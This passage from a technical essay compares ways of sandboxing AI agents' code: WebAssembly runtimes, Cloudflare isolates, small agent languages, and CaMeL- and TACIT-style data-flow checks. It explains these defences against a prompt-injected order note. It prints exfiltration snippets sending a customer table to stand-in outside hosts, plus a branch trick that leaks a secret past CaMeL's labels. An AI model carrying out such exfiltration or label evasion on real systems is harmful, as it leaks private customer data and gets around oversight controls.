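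For changes on disk, the claim mostly holds, provided that the list also includes compiled modules and downloaded packages. The list shows only what the program could have changed, so an entry for the orders folder doesn't show whether the program changed `orders.csv`. More importantly, the model fills in `dirs` itself. If the customer's note leads it to request the clerk's home folder, the host opens that folder with the clerk's authority, much as Hardy's compiler opened BILL. The developer suggests that a supervisor could reject folders outside the task's workspace. Without that check, the log records the agent's access without limiting it.

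The list also doesn't cover what the agent could have read. Rust source code can copy another file's contents into a program during compilation, and the compiler runs outside Wasmtime. Unless the host also restricts the compiler, a program could include the customer list when it is compiled and print it later, even if its module has no open folders.

### Isolates and bindings

JavaScript can work similarly, because the language itself has no commands for opening files or network connections. The program that runs it supplies them, as a browser supplies `fetch` for web requests. Google Chrome's JavaScript engine is called V8, and an isolate is an instance of V8 with its own memory.

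Cloudflare, which runs customers' code in its data centers, has used isolates for its Workers platform since it launched. Varda, Pai and Gupta, in *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, describe an extension called Dynamic Workers, which lets a program on the platform start a new isolate for code that a model has just written. For the orders task, the host's side could look roughly like this:

```
env.LOADER.load({
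  mainModule: "totals.js",
  modules: { "totals.js": codeFromModel },
  env: { ORDERS: pendingOrders, MANAGER: managerMail },
  globalOutbound: null
})
```

The last setting blocks the network, so `fetch` produces an error. `ORDERS` and `MANAGER` are bindings, objects that the host has written and passed in. The model's code can call their methods:

```
const orders = await env.ORDERS.list();
const total = orders.reduce((sum, o) => sum + o.amount, 0);
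await env.MANAGER.send("Pending orders: $" + total);
```

The first line sends a message to the host, which queries the database with its own password and returns the pending orders. The isolate adds them up, and the last line has the host email the result to the manager. The code never receives the database password or the mail credentials, so it can't leak them. It also has no object for the customers table and can't specify a different recipient.

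These two bindings are the attenuated wrappers from the original orders example. If the host supplied API keys instead, the code would need a network connection to use them.

The host can also let the code make web requests and inspect each one on the way out, adding credentials where necessary. With a binding, the host instead writes only the methods it allows. Varda and colleagues generally prefer bindings because a filter has to interpret every header and parameter that could change what a request does. Varda and Pai point out in *Code Mode* that filtering also makes the model's task harder, since it has to guess which requests the filter will block.

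### Why agents write code instead of making single calls

Varda and Pai introduced Code Mode in 2025. It turns an agent's tools into functions in TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with type annotations, and gives the model a single tool that runs code. Their first reason is that models have seen a huge amount of real code in training, while the tool calls they have seen are mostly contrived examples. In their experience, agents can therefore handle more tools, and more complex ones, when the tools look like an ordinary programming interface.

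Their other reason is that a single call returns its full result to the model, which often does nothing with it except copy part into the next call. Code can pass the result along directly. In an example from Varda and colleagues, an agent fetches the last 1,000 messages from a chat room and keeps only Alice's. The code filters the messages in the isolate, so the model receives only hers.

This can also help with prompt injection, although Cloudflare presents it mainly as a way to save time and money. The model never sees the customer's instruction if the program adds up the orders without printing their notes, but it does see the instruction if it first prints a few rows to check what the data looks like.

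Cloudflare has published several figures:

- An isolate starts in a few milliseconds and uses a few megabytes of memory. Varda and colleagues put this at around 100 times faster than a typical container, with 10 to 100 times less memory.
- Converting an MCP server's tools into a TypeScript interface can cut the number of tokens, the units of text that a model processes, by 81%.
- Cloudflare's own MCP server covers more than 2,500 operations, according to Tomé and Curry, in *Code Mode*, with only two tools. Describing them takes about 1,000 tokens.
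- Each new piece of code costs $0.002 a day to load, on top of normal computing charges, so 1,000 one-off programs would cost $2. Cloudflare waived this fee during the beta.

The comparison with containers is plausible, but Sandlock also starts a process in milliseconds, so isolates are not much faster than a good process sandbox. The 81% is a single figure for converting a server, and an agent's savings will depend on how many tools it has and how much data passes between them. The orders task needs only two calls, so it would save little.

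Varda and colleagues report that one customer, the app builder Zite, handles millions of executions a day on Dynamic Workers. But Cloudflare labels the software package for Code Mode experimental and advises caution in production.

### Hardened JavaScript and Endo

A binding gives a whole program access to a resource, and the program often includes third-party libraries. If the orders program uses a library to format currency, that library's code runs in the same isolate and may be able to reach the same bindings.

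A malicious library can also interfere less directly, because all the code in an ordinary JavaScript program shares built-in objects, including the one that holds the methods for lists. The library could replace the standard `reduce` method with a version that works normally but keeps a copy of every list. If the main program then uses `reduce` to total the orders, the library gets a copy of them.

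Hardened JavaScript limits what code can reach and change within a single program. *SES*, the documentation for a package that adds it to existing JavaScript engines, describes three main functions. `lockdown` freezes the shared built-in objects, so no code can replace a built-in method such as `reduce`. `Compartment` creates a separate environment for a piece of code, with its own global variables and without `fetch` or anything else that reaches outside. `harden` freezes an object before the host passes it in, so the code that receives it can call its methods but can't alter them.

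The host can then divide authority finely. Agoric, a company that uses the system for smart contracts, gives the example of counting people in a room. A counter has one function that adds and another that subtracts. The entrance guard receives only the first and the exit guard only the second, so neither can do the other's job. The host could similarly give the currency library only a number to format.

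Compartments also remove access to the current time and the random number generator by default. Two pieces of code that share a random number generator can use it to pass information to each other.

According to the documentation, code in a compartment can run forever or use up all the memory, because compartments have nothing like Wasmtime's fuel. The trusted base includes the JavaScript engine, the operating system and any JavaScript that runs before `lockdown`. Three engineers spent four weeks assessing the package in June 2021 and found no previously unknown vulnerabilities. That result is encouraging, but it is more than five years old.

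Endo builds on Hardened JavaScript and extends its object references to other processes and computers. In a demonstration called Endo Familiar, an AI agent starts with almost no authority. It can read one document, which contains its instructions, and it receives further capabilities as the task requires. Under Miller's rules, the document is an endowment and the later capabilities are introductions.

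The working prototype shows that an agent can start with no access, but it doesn't measure how often such an agent gets stuck or how carefully people consider its requests for access after the first several.

### Programs that won't run

A runtime can withhold access this thoroughly because it runs only code in formats it supports. An agent can't run `awk`, Git or a project's existing test program in an isolate, and it can run them in Wasmtime only if someone has compiled them to WebAssembly. Many popular Python packages contain native code (instructions for a particular processor), which must also be compiled to WebAssembly.

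`wasm_agent.py` had this problem with packages. It needed a library to read JSON, a common data format, and downloaded one called `rjson`. That library required an experimental version of the Rust compiler, so the agent switched to `tinyjson`, which worked and has only four files and no dependencies. Packages don't work if they run their own scripts during compilation or bring in a long chain of other packages, and the agent's instructions tell it to choose something simpler.

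Dynamic Workers can run Python and WebAssembly as well as JavaScript, but Varda and colleagues say that JavaScript loads and runs much faster for short programs. They say the only drawback compared with containers is having to write JavaScript, which they argue hardly matters because models can write any major language. Their argument is reasonable for a program that totals orders, but it doesn't help an agent that has to repair a large Python project and run its tests. Cloudflare offers containers for work that needs a full Linux system.

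### Flaws in the runtime

WASI's documentation describes its protection as stronger than typical process isolation, because it restricts a module regardless of what the host process is allowed to do. But the protection holds only if the runtime has no serious bugs. A module normally runs inside the host's process, so if it escapes the sandbox, it may be able to read the host's memory, including any passwords there.

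Bytecode Alliance's *Wasmtime's April 9, 2026 Security Advisories* (2026) announced 12 vulnerabilities, three times as many as in all of 2025. The maintainers had found 11 of them in three weeks with the help of language models. Two were critical and could let a module escape its sandbox.

One of these two bugs was in Cranelift, Wasmtime's default compiler, and affected ARM processors. Researchers had formally verified the relevant part of Cranelift, meaning they had checked mathematically that its translation rules were correct. But a later version introduced the bug, and nobody had updated the mathematical model to match. When the maintainers updated it, it also revealed the bug that the language models had found.

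In April, the maintainers said that neither critical flaw affected Cranelift on x86-64, the most common combination in production. In October, they fixed two more critical flaws in Cranelift, one of which affected every type of processor, but only in older versions of Wasmtime. The Hacker News' *Two Critical Wasmtime Flaws Could Let Malicious WebAssembly Modules Escape Sandboxes* (2026) noted that the maintainers had reported no attacks. OffSeq's *wasmtime · Cranelift* (2026) lists another critical flaw, published on December 4.

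An attacker can exploit the October flaws only if Wasmtime compiles a module the attacker controls. The flaws are therefore most serious for services that run other people's code. An agent's host is in much the same position because it compiles whatever the model writes, which an injected instruction may influence.

The functions the host supplies can have bugs too. Alpine Linux's *CVE-2026-54786* describes one in Wasmtime's function for renumbering open files. The function updated the module's table but not the host's, so files stayed open in the host after the module had finished with them. A module that called it repeatedly could tie up more and more of the host's resources without escaping the sandbox.

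V8 has a similar problem. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that its security bugs are more common than those in typical hypervisors. A comparison with hardware separation should weigh this weakness against the low overhead of isolates. To reduce the risk, Cloudflare installs V8 fixes within hours and runs the isolates inside a second sandbox. A host that runs Wasmtime on a developer's machine can also put the whole runtime in one of the process sandboxes described earlier.

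### Host functions that are too broad

Even a perfect runtime enforces only the limits in the functions it receives. Code in Varda and Pai's Code Mode sandbox, which they describe as totally isolated from the internet, can't open a connection itself. But their sample tools for reading Cloudflare's documentation include `fetch_generic_url_content`, which retrieves a page from any web address. Code that had read a customer's name could put it in an address on an attacker's site and call that function. The tool server would then send the name to the attacker when it requested the page. The function respects `robots.txt`, a file that lists which pages on a site automated visitors should avoid, but an attacker's site would be unlikely to block the request.

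Cloudflare's 1,000-token interface is another case where a short description can make an agent's access look smaller than it is. Carey's *Code Mode* presents the interface as a way to leave more of the model's input free for the task, and it does that. But its two tools reach 2,500 operations, so they can do as much damage as 2,500 separate tools unless the account behind them has narrower permissions.

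Hardened JavaScript also leaves this responsibility with the host. Its documentation calls code in an empty compartment a "glorified calculator" and says that once the host passes objects in, it must maintain whatever protections it needs. Languages built for agents can restrict what a program may express, but their programs still have to call tools that somebody has written.

If the host gave a Dynamic Worker the clerk's two original tools as bindings, a program that followed the customer's note could steal the customer list with two lines of code, even if `globalOutbound` were `null` and every password were hidden.

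## Small languages for combining tools

Cloudflare's isolates accept any JavaScript the model writes, so the protection depends on all of V8 working correctly. Some designers instead give the agent a much smaller language. Its programs can do arithmetic, filter lists and build text, but they can affect the outside world only by calling tools the host supplies. As with Code Mode, the aim is to combine several tool calls in one program. The interpreter, which runs the code, can omit everything such programs don't need.

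### Starting from nothing

The opposite approach is to start with ordinary Python and block the dangerous parts. Blocking names such as `open` and `import` isn't enough, because Python lets a program inspect its own objects. Starting from an empty list, a program can find the list's class, then the class that all others derive from, and then every class the interpreter has loaded. Some of these classes can open files or start other programs, and a defender has to block every route to them.

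Hermetic's *Threat Model* describes a tool that blocks unwanted access from inside a Python process but "is not a security boundary". Hermetic suits tests that must not touch the network, and plugins or models that misbehave but aren't malicious. But an agent that has read the customer's note may be writing code for an attacker.

PTC-Lisp takes the other route. It is a small subset of Clojure, a modern form of Lisp, and runs on the open-source project PtcRunner. In PtcRunner's *Why I Built a Lisp for AI Agents*, the developer asks, "what if the language itself was the constraint?" PTC-Lisp has no functions for opening files or network connections, no way to import other code, and no `eval`, the function that runs text as a program, though programs can still read the system clock. The host adds tools one at a time, all with names that begin with `tool/`.

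If a program calls `(tool/customers)` and the host hasn't granted a tool of that name, the program gets the error `unknown_tool`. Clojure's `slurp` function, which reads a file, is also an unknown word in PTC-Lisp. The model can write any name, but the interpreter looks up tool names only in the table that the host filled in for this program. A tool name therefore works like a position in Dennis and Van Horn's C-list, except that people can read it.

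### The orders task as a program

Suppose the host grants two narrow tools. One returns pending orders and the other emails the manager. The model could then write this:

```
(def orders (tool/pending-orders))
(def total (sum-by :amount orders))
(tool/email-manager {:text (str "Pending orders: $" total)})
(return total)
```

Lisp function calls are written in parentheses, with the function's name first. `def` stores a value under a name, `sum-by` adds up one field across a list of records, and `str` joins pieces of text.

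The interpreter first parses the program into nested lists. If there is an extra closing parenthesis, it stops here with an error that gives the line and column. The interpreter then checks the program without running it. This check would report an undefined variable if the model had written `totl` on the last line, or an error if it had given `if` too many parts. PtcRunner lets a host run these two stages alone, and by default limits them to five seconds and a megabyte of source code.

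The interpreter then evaluates the program. Because the interpreter contains no database code, on the first line it calls a host function that queries the database with the host's own password and returns three records. `sum-by` adds the amounts, giving running totals of 1,200, 1,650 and 4,000. On the third line, the interpreter passes the host a field named `text` containing "Pending orders: $4000". The host adds the manager's address and sends the message. Finally, the model receives the number 4000 and none of the orders.

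In PtcRunner's *PTC-Lisp Language Specification*, `sum-by` skips any record that lacks the field being added and raises no error, which could make this result wrong. If a $450 order were missing its amount, the email would show $3550 with no sign of a problem. The language has no way to catch an error and continue, so its designer made many functions tolerate bad data. However, an amount stored as text, such as "450", does cause an error.

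### Time and memory limits

A program with no dangerous functions can still loop forever or fill the computer's memory. PtcRunner runs each PTC-Lisp program in a separate Erlang process. Erlang is a programming language whose runtime can hold thousands of these small processes, each with its own memory, inside one operating-system process.

By default, a program can run for one second and use about 10 megabytes of memory. It can start up to eight parallel workers, each with its own 10 megabytes, so together they can use about 90 megabytes. Data that the host supplies at the start doesn't count toward the program's limit, but data that a tool returns does. If the orders tool returned ten million rows, the runtime would stop the process and send the model the reason, and the model could then request fewer rows.

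Erlang checks a process's memory only when it cleans up unused data, so a process can briefly exceed its memory limit. PtcRunner's documentation warns that this limit applies to individual Erlang processes, not the whole runtime. It recommends a second memory limit from the operating system or a container when users may attack one another. The documentation is inconsistent about whether loops have a separate limit by default, but the time limit stops an endless loop either way.

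When a host uses the interpreter directly, a program can also make as many tool calls as fit into its one-second limit, unless the host sets a maximum.

Other interpreters handle limits differently. According to Pydantic's *Monty* documentation, Monty, a small Python interpreter, raises an error before it tries to allocate memory for `'x' * 10**12`, a string of a trillion characters. In languages with exception handling, a program might catch the error for exceeding a limit and carry on. Littrs, another small Python interpreter, makes such errors impossible to catch.

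### When the tools are too broad

As with Cloudflare's bindings, none of this helps if the host registers the clerk's two original tools. This program steals the customer list:

```
(tool/send-mail
  {:to "outside@example.com"
   :text (json/generate-string
           (tool/run-query {:sql "SELECT * FROM customers"}))})
```

Every name in the program exists, and every argument has the right type. It finishes within a second unless the database is slow and needs little memory unless the list is very long. A limit of two tool calls wouldn't stop it, and a lower limit would also block the legitimate program, which needs two.

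PtcRunner's specification lists data theft among its security concerns and relies on the host to control the tools and audit their use. The audit log would show the query and the outside address, but only after the message had been sent. Restricting what either tool can do would help more. If the program could run any query but email only the manager, it could not send the customer list to anyone else.

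The host can also create a security hole by building programs out of text. For example, if it pastes a customer's name straight into the source code of a program template, a customer could add a tool call to the program by entering a "name" that contains a quotation mark and some parentheses. PtcRunner's specification advises hosts to pass such values separately, as data that the program reads under a fixed name. Web developers use the same technique to keep form entries from changing their database queries.

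### Concurrency without threads

Runlet is a language for tasks that need many similar calls. Suppose the clerk also wants to know, for each pending order, whether the item is in stock and what delivery would cost:

```
orders = shop.pending_orders()
checked = for order in orders limit 2 {
    stock = warehouse.stock(order.number)
    quote = courier.quote(order.number)
    return { number: order.number, stock, quote }
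}
return checked
```

Runlet determines which calls can run at the same time from the values each call uses, so the program doesn't have to specify this. Both lookups need an order number, so they wait for the list of orders, then start together because neither needs the other's result. `limit 2` allows two orders to be in progress at once. If every call takes one second, the seven calls finish in three seconds: one for the list, one for the first two orders, and one for the third. The model writes one program instead of making seven requests.

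The host registers each tool with a schema that describes the arguments the tool accepts and the result it returns. Runlet checks the whole program against these schemas before it calls any tool. A misspelled tool name on the last line therefore can't leave a task half finished, which could happen in a language that detects such errors only at run time.

In return, the programmer gives up functions, classes, imports, variables that change, and some control over execution. Runlet skips any "pure" call (one the host has labeled as having no side effects) if nothing uses its result. It always runs calls that have side effects, but it relies on the host's labels to identify them. If a host mislabeled its mail tool as pure, Runlet could skip sending an email and give only a warning.

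`limit 2` caps only the number of orders in progress at once, so a program with 10,000 orders would still make 20,001 calls. Runlet is at version 0.1.0, and its developers list cancellation among the features they haven't built.

They justify the general approach with a case study from AgentKit, a framework for running agents, which used the existing language Lua. In six scenarios, letting the model write a program cut costs by 38–77% without reducing accuracy. It worked best when each item in a list needed a lookup, and it could be counterproductive in open-ended investigations. That makes sense, because an investigator has to read one result before choosing the next step, and a program written in advance doesn't pause for that.

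### Programs that always end

safescript gives up more than the others and promises more in return. It has no loops or recursion, so every program ends. A program can apply a function to each item in a list, select items, or combine them into one value, but it can't sort them. The interpreter translates each program into a fixed graph of operations, with arrows showing where each piece of data goes.

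A safescript program must name every network host it contacts and every secret it reads as literal text in its source, so it can't compute these names while it runs. Before the program runs, safescript can therefore produce a "signature" that lists every secret the program reads, every host it contacts, and which data may reach which destination.

Suppose the company offers its orders and mail as web services. The honest program's signature would include these lines:

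```
hosts: data.example.com, mail.example.com
data reaching mail.example.com: from data.example.com
```

If the customer's note led the model to upload the list to `evil.example`, that address would appear in the signature, and the host could reject the program without running it. The same check applies to imported code. A program declares which hosts, secrets and data flows a library may use, and the build fails if an update to the library adds another. For an agent that installs skills written by strangers, this is a useful protection. (Researchers have built related checks into the type system of Scala, a full programming language.)

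The signature wouldn't reveal the original theft, because the theft uses the same two hosts as the honest program and data still flows from the first to the second. A list of approved hosts wouldn't prevent the theft for the same reason. Only the network host has to be literal text, so the path that selects customers and the message that names the recipient don't appear in the signature. safescript describes its analysis as exact, but this is true only of the labels in the signature.

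The signature also includes upper limits on time and memory. Each operation declares how much it may use, and safescript adds up these amounts. The total is only as reliable as the declarations. Lists are a further problem, because a program might apply a function to every order that a server returns, and the number of orders isn't known before the program runs. The documentation describes no maximum. According to the documentation, the interpreter also processes such a list in parallel, so a list of 10,000 orders could produce 10,000 simultaneous web requests. The program would end, as promised, but a host would still want a time limit and a cap on requests.

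A safescript program also receives the text of each secret it reads, whereas a Cloudflare binding keeps the password in the host. However, the safescript program's signature shows whether a secret may reach the program's result and, through that result, the model.

### Keeping Python's syntax

Monty, an interpreter from the software company Pydantic, is written in Rust and runs a subset of Python. In the company's example, a model writes a program to calculate how long a chocolate bar could power a 10-watt bulb. The program calls `nutrition('chocolate bar')`, a function the host provides. The interpreter passes the call to the host, which returns 230 kilocalories, and the program calculates the answer, 26.7 hours. The program can't reach the network or the host's files. Another project, interpretthis, is a similar interpreter that gives Python programs outside access only through the host's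 tools.

Monty can save a program's complete state and resume it later because the program stops at each call to the host. When the orders program tries to send its email, the host could save the program's state, ask the clerk for approval, and resume the program the next morning without keeping anything running overnight.

Monty lacks much of what makes Python useful. Willison (2026) observed in *Running Pydantic's Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly* that it didn't support classes in February. Pydantic promised to add classes and `match` statements and to expand Monty's small subset of the standard library, but said that Monty would probably never support third-party packages. Without packages, an agent can add up orders, but it can't use the usual Python tools for charts or statistics.

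The company's documentation compares startup times:

| | New sandbox | Ten commands in it |
|---|---|---|
| Monty | 0.8 ms | 0.4 ms |
| WebAssembly in Wasmtime | 16 ms | 180 ms |
| Docker on the same machine | 195 ms | 700 ms |
| Remote sandbox service | 1,500 ms | 400 ms |

The comparison favors Monty in two ways. Monty takes a waiting process from a pool the application has already created, while the others start from scratch. Monty also keeps its state between commands, while the others rerun all earlier commands each time, so ten commands require 55 executions. Pydantic states both conditions. A host could keep a pool of containers as well, but Monty would probably still be faster.

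Pydantic's *Security Model* says that Monty relies on its interpreter alone, with no container, system-call filter or virtual machine around it. Pydantic pays people to find ways out, and Plushcap's *Hack Monty 2* reports that attackers escaped within 48 hours in the first round, in April 2026. Pydantic fixed the flaws and doubled the reward. Prefect, which runs Monty in its own software, helped fund the second round because, as it said in Pydantic's announcement, with an embedded interpreter "a sandbox escape is a host compromise". By the third round, Pydantic was inviting people to attack a live server.

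Attackers found flaws in Monty and Pydantic repaired them, which should count in Monty's favor. Nobody appears to have attacked the other three interpreters so publicly. But the attackers' quick success weakens the claim that safescript programs need no sandbox because the language contains nothing dangerous. Monty's language has no file or network access either, and the weakness was in the code that implements it. Monty now runs programs in separate worker processes, which a host can restrict with Landlock or seccomp with little overhead.

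### Do models need a language they already know?

The usual objection to a new language is that models have read far more Python and JavaScript. In *A Language For Agents*, Ronacher (2026) agrees that agents do much better in languages from their training data, but in his experience documentation and build tools matter too. Agents manage passably in Zig, a less common language that changes often, if someone points them to the right documentation. They struggle with Apple's Swift, despite having seen plenty of it, because its build tools are awkward. He also warns that models easily get Lisp wrong because they lose track of how many parentheses they have closed.

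PTC-Lisp's developer expected models to write the language less well for lack of training data, and tested this. In one set of 100 benchmark runs, Google's Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite Preview, a small and inexpensive model, passed 95. Another agent, also writing PTC-Lisp, searched the logs for the cause of the five failures. It first concluded that every run had passed, but after further checks it traced the failures to `.isBefore` and `.isAfter`, which compare dates. The developer confirmed the diagnosis and fixed the problem, and the same benchmarks then passed. The current language supports both methods.

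These failures happened because the model knew ordinary Clojure better than the subset, not because it knew too little Lisp. Its date comparisons would have worked in ordinary Clojure, which can use Java methods. By its own count, PtcRunner supports 211 of the 534 names in Clojure's core library, so a model that writes normal Clojure will sometimes use a missing one. Monty has the same problem with Python. Basing a small language on a familiar one helps the model with syntax but also leads it to use features that are missing.

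The project has published larger tests as well, all from 2026:

| Month | Model | Passed |
|---|---|---|
| January | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 95 of 95 |
| January | Gemini 2.5 Flash | 88 of 95 |
| January | DeepSeek v3 | 88 of 95 |
| March | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 897 of 900 |
| March | Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite Preview | 895 of 900 |
| May | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 149 of 150 |
| May | Gemini 3.1 Flash Lite | 149 of 150 |

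The January results come from PtcRunner's *Benchmark Evaluation* (2026), which advises taking them "with a grain of salt". The March run is the largest, with 30 tasks repeated 30 times for each model. The tasks range from counting and averaging to searching documents over several turns. According to PtcRunner (2026), one of the two failures in May was a type error in a task that allowed only one attempt. In the other, the program ran properly but the model chose the wrong document, which could have happened in any language.

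These results are good evidence that even small models can write short PTC-Lisp programs. They don't show that models write PTC-Lisp as well as Python, because the project hasn't published results for the same tasks and tools in both languages. The developer also adds functions when models try to use missing ones in the benchmarks. This is a sensible way to improve the language, but it means later scores partly reflect changes made to suit the benchmarks.

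Most of the evidence for small languages comes from tests their own authors ran, which weakens it. The projects are also young. Runlet and safescript are both at version 0.1.0, and PtcRunner carries the warning "Expect bugs".

Error messages probably explain much of PTC-Lisp's success. If a program calls `clojure.string/capitalize`, which PTC-Lisp lacks, the interpreter reports that `capitalize` isn't available and lists the text functions that are. In the May tests, models that had tried missing functions for cutting up text switched to `subs`, the supported one. Others had nested shorthand functions, which PTC-Lisp forbids, and rewrote the code in the longer form. Willison makes the same argument for Monty, saying that a model can try another approach after an error shows that classes aren't supported, because models are very good at working from error messages.

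Each correction requires another request to the model, and a second attempt can repeat an action the first already took. When a PTC-Lisp program fails in an agent session, PtcRunner discards the values the program stored, which the specification calls "safe for retry loops", but it can't withdraw an email the program has already sent. If the orders program emailed the manager and then failed on its last line, the model would receive an error, correct the program and run it again, and the manager would get the $4,000 total twice.

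## Checking data flow before or while a program runs

The Lisp program that mailed out the customer list made two permitted calls, and the harm came from passing the result of one to the other. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao et al., 2026) describes the same problem in process sandboxes. An agent can read a private file with a permitted system call, then send the text to an outside model over a permitted connection, without violating the sandbox's restrictions.

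Narrower tools are enough when the host knows exactly what a task needs. But suppose the clerk asks the agent to write to every customer whose order is late. The agent now needs both the customers table and the ability to email outsiders, so the useful rule is that a customer's record may go only to that customer or to staff. Information flow control enforces such rules by tracking where data came from and where it may go, and it does the same for anything a program computes from that data.

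Some of these rules protect secrets, as this one does. Others stop untrusted data from deciding something important, such as who receives a payment. The strictest standard for secrets is noninterference, which compares two runs of a program that differ only in their secret inputs:

same public inputs ⇒ same public outputs

A program that emails the word "rich" to a stranger whenever a bank balance exceeds $10,000 fails this test, even though it never sends the balance.

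### Labels that travel with the data

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, from 2025, checks data flow while a program runs. It builds on a two-model design that Willison proposed in 2023. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) explains that CaMeL's privileged model sees the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model reads untrusted text and extracts what the program needs, but it has no tools. An interpreter in the host runs the program and makes the tool calls.

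Suppose the clerk asks the agent to send a delivery update to the contact address in an order's notes. The privileged model might write this:

```
order = get_order(2)
address = extract("contact email", order.notes)
send_mail(address, "Your order will arrive on Monday.")
```

In the second line, the quarantined model extracts the address. Nothing in the note can add a fourth line, because the privileged model finished the program before either model read the note. At worst, the note makes the quarantined model return the wrong address.

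To deal with that, CaMeL's interpreter labels each value with its sources and the people who may read it. CaMeL's developers call these labels capabilities, although the labels describe data and don't give anyone access to anything. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that allows or denies the call based on the tool's name, its arguments and their labels. One policy might require that a recipient's address come from the clerk. Another might check that a message's recipient is among its permitted readers, which would stop a program from sending the customer list to an outside address. Hosts without CaMeL can also check where a single call's arguments came from.

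The first policy would deny the delivery update above whether the note held the customer's real address or an attacker's, because the label records only that the address came from a note.

Edoardo Debenedetti led the work on AgentDojo, the benchmark that most research in this area uses, before he led the work on CaMeL. AgentDojo has 97 user tasks in four suites, which simulate a bank account, an office workspace, the chat service Slack and a travel service. Each attack hides an instruction in something a tool returns. The benchmark measures how many tasks the agent completes (utility) and how often the attacker gets what the instruction asked for. CaMeL's defence doesn't need the model to recognize an attack. According to figures that Odersky and colleagues reprint, CaMeL with OpenAI's o4-mini-high completed between 62.5% and 81.4% of tasks, depending on the suite, and one attack in 963 succeeded.

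### What later work found in CaMeL

In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's 16 banking tasks, three times each, with two newer models. With its policies on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 runs with each model, or 37.5%. With the policies off, it completed 32 with one model and 34 with the other, or 67% and 71%. With only 16 tasks, the margin of error on the 37.5% is about 27 points either way, but the policies had a similar effect on both models. The policies made some tasks impossible. For example, an agent can't pay a bill if the account number is in a file and the payment tool rejects data from files.

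The reruns also help explain why so few attacks succeed on AgentDojo. Each of the 16 banking tasks is paired with nine attacks, making 144 pairs. In 97 of these, the attack needs a tool call that no sensible program for the user's task would contain, so writing the program first normally defeats it. Only the other 47 pairs really test the labels.

One task in that first group asks the agent to follow the instructions in a file precisely. With the policies off, the privileged model wrote a loop that chose a tool based on the file's contents, which gave control back to whoever had written the file. Two attacks unexpectedly succeeded this way.

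Garby and colleagues also found gaps in the labels themselves. One involves a trick that researchers have known about for decades, and a program that uses it could look like this:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > 10000: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_mail("outside@example.com", "rich")
```

If the balance is $12,000, the third line sets `tmp` to false and labels it secret. The fourth line then does nothing. CaMeL changes a variable's label only on the branch the program takes, so `rich` is still true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is $8,000, the third line does nothing, the fourth sets `rich` to false, and no email goes out. The stranger learns which side of $10,000 the balance is on, and the labels don't show the leak.

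This leaks only one bit. But CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary retry loop that doesn't track labels, so an attacker who could make the loop repeat the leak could extract a whole secret bit by bit. The attacker would need some influence over the privileged model to get such a program written. CaMeL's design makes that hard when there is one agent and one user, but it is easier when agents pass work to each other. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) describes an injection that starts in a database and passes from one agent to another, whose planning model reads it directly.

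Garby and colleagues propose LLMbda, a small language that carries labels through every step of a program. They give a computer-checked proof that its interpreter satisfies a form of noninterference. With the checks always on, an agent they wrote in LLMbda completed 75% of the banking runs with GPT-5.2. Across three models, only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded.

Some of that utility comes from an exception called endorsement. Before it has read anything, the model that writes the program may mark a particular piece of untrusted data as acceptable for a particular use. Without endorsement, utility with one of the models fell from 75% to 62.5%. Both successful attacks used the same task, in which the user asks the agent to make whatever payment a file specifies and the attacker has rewritten the file. Because the user did ask the agent to follow the file, labels can't prevent the attack unless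 the system forbids the task altogether.

### Types that list what code can use

TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types) checks a program before running it. Odersky and colleagues at EPFL built it on the programming language Scala 3. It runs as an MCP server, so agents such as Claude Code can use it without modification. The agent sends TACIT pieces of Scala code. A compiler checks each piece, and a local interpreter runs the ones that pass. The code can access files, commands and the network only through a library of capabilities.

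An ordinary type describes the shape of some data, such as text (`String`) or a whole number (`Int`). Scala's experimental "capture checking" adds a list of the capabilities that a value can use, called its capture set. If `f` is an open file, a function that writes text to it has this type:

`String ->{f} Unit`

It takes text, returns nothing useful (`Unit`), and may use `f`. The compiler works out what the function's body uses and compares this with any type the programmer has declared, so an agent can't hide the file by leaving it off the list. A function of type `String -> Unit`, with no braces, has an empty capture set, so it is pure and can have no side effects. (A double arrow, `String => Unit`, allows any capability at all.)

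TACIT puts secrets in a wrapper named `Classified`. Someone marks certain folders as classified, and reading a file in one of them returns `Classified[String]` instead of `String`. The agent's code has no way to take the text out. It can only hand the wrapper a function to apply to the text, using `map`:

`def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]`

The single arrow in `T -> U` means that `map` accepts only pure functions. `map` returns the result in a new wrapper.

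### An accepted line and a rejected one

Suppose the customer list is in a classified folder, and the agent's code already has a network capability named `net`. It reads the list like this:

`val customers = readClassified("/data/secret/customers.csv")`

Then it counts the customers, one to a line:

`val count = customers.map(text => text.count(_ == '\n'))`

The function in parentheses counts line breaks and uses no capabilities. Its type, `String -> Int`, fits what `map` requires, so the compiler accepts the line. The variable `count` holds a `Classified[Int]`, because even the number of customers might be confidential.

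Next, the agent follows an injected instruction and tries to upload the list:

`customers.map(text => httpPost("https://outside.example", text))`

The library's `httpPost` function needs the network capability, so the compiler gives it the type `String ->{net} String`. But `map` requires a function of type `String -> String`, whose empty capture set doesn't allow `net`. The compiler therefore rejects the code before it runs, and the agent gets an error message naming the capability.

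Passing `customers` to `httpPost` outside `map` also fails, because `httpPost` accepts text and `customers` isn't text. Printing from inside `map` fails too, because it also needs a capability. In the EPFL tests, one agent read a classified GitHub key and tried to print it from inside `map`, and the compiler stopped it.

This would also stop the theft in the orders example if somebody had marked the customers table as classified. The mail tool can send to anyone, but it accepts only plain text. If the clerk wanted to send classified text to the manager, the library's author would have to write a tool that accepts wrapped text and sends it only to the manager, much like the attenuated mail wrapper.

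Pure functions are enough for counting and sorting, but many tasks require a model to read the secret. For these, TACIT offers a second language model that the company trusts, usually one it runs on its own machines. The agent's code can send this model wrapped text and receive a wrapped answer. For example, the code could have the trusted model summarize a classified contract and then save the summary in a classified file, without the model that wrote the code seeing the contract or the summary.

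### Access that ends with its block

The library grants access for the length of one block of code. This block asks for the `/data` folder and receives a capability named `fs`:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("orders.csv").read()
}
```

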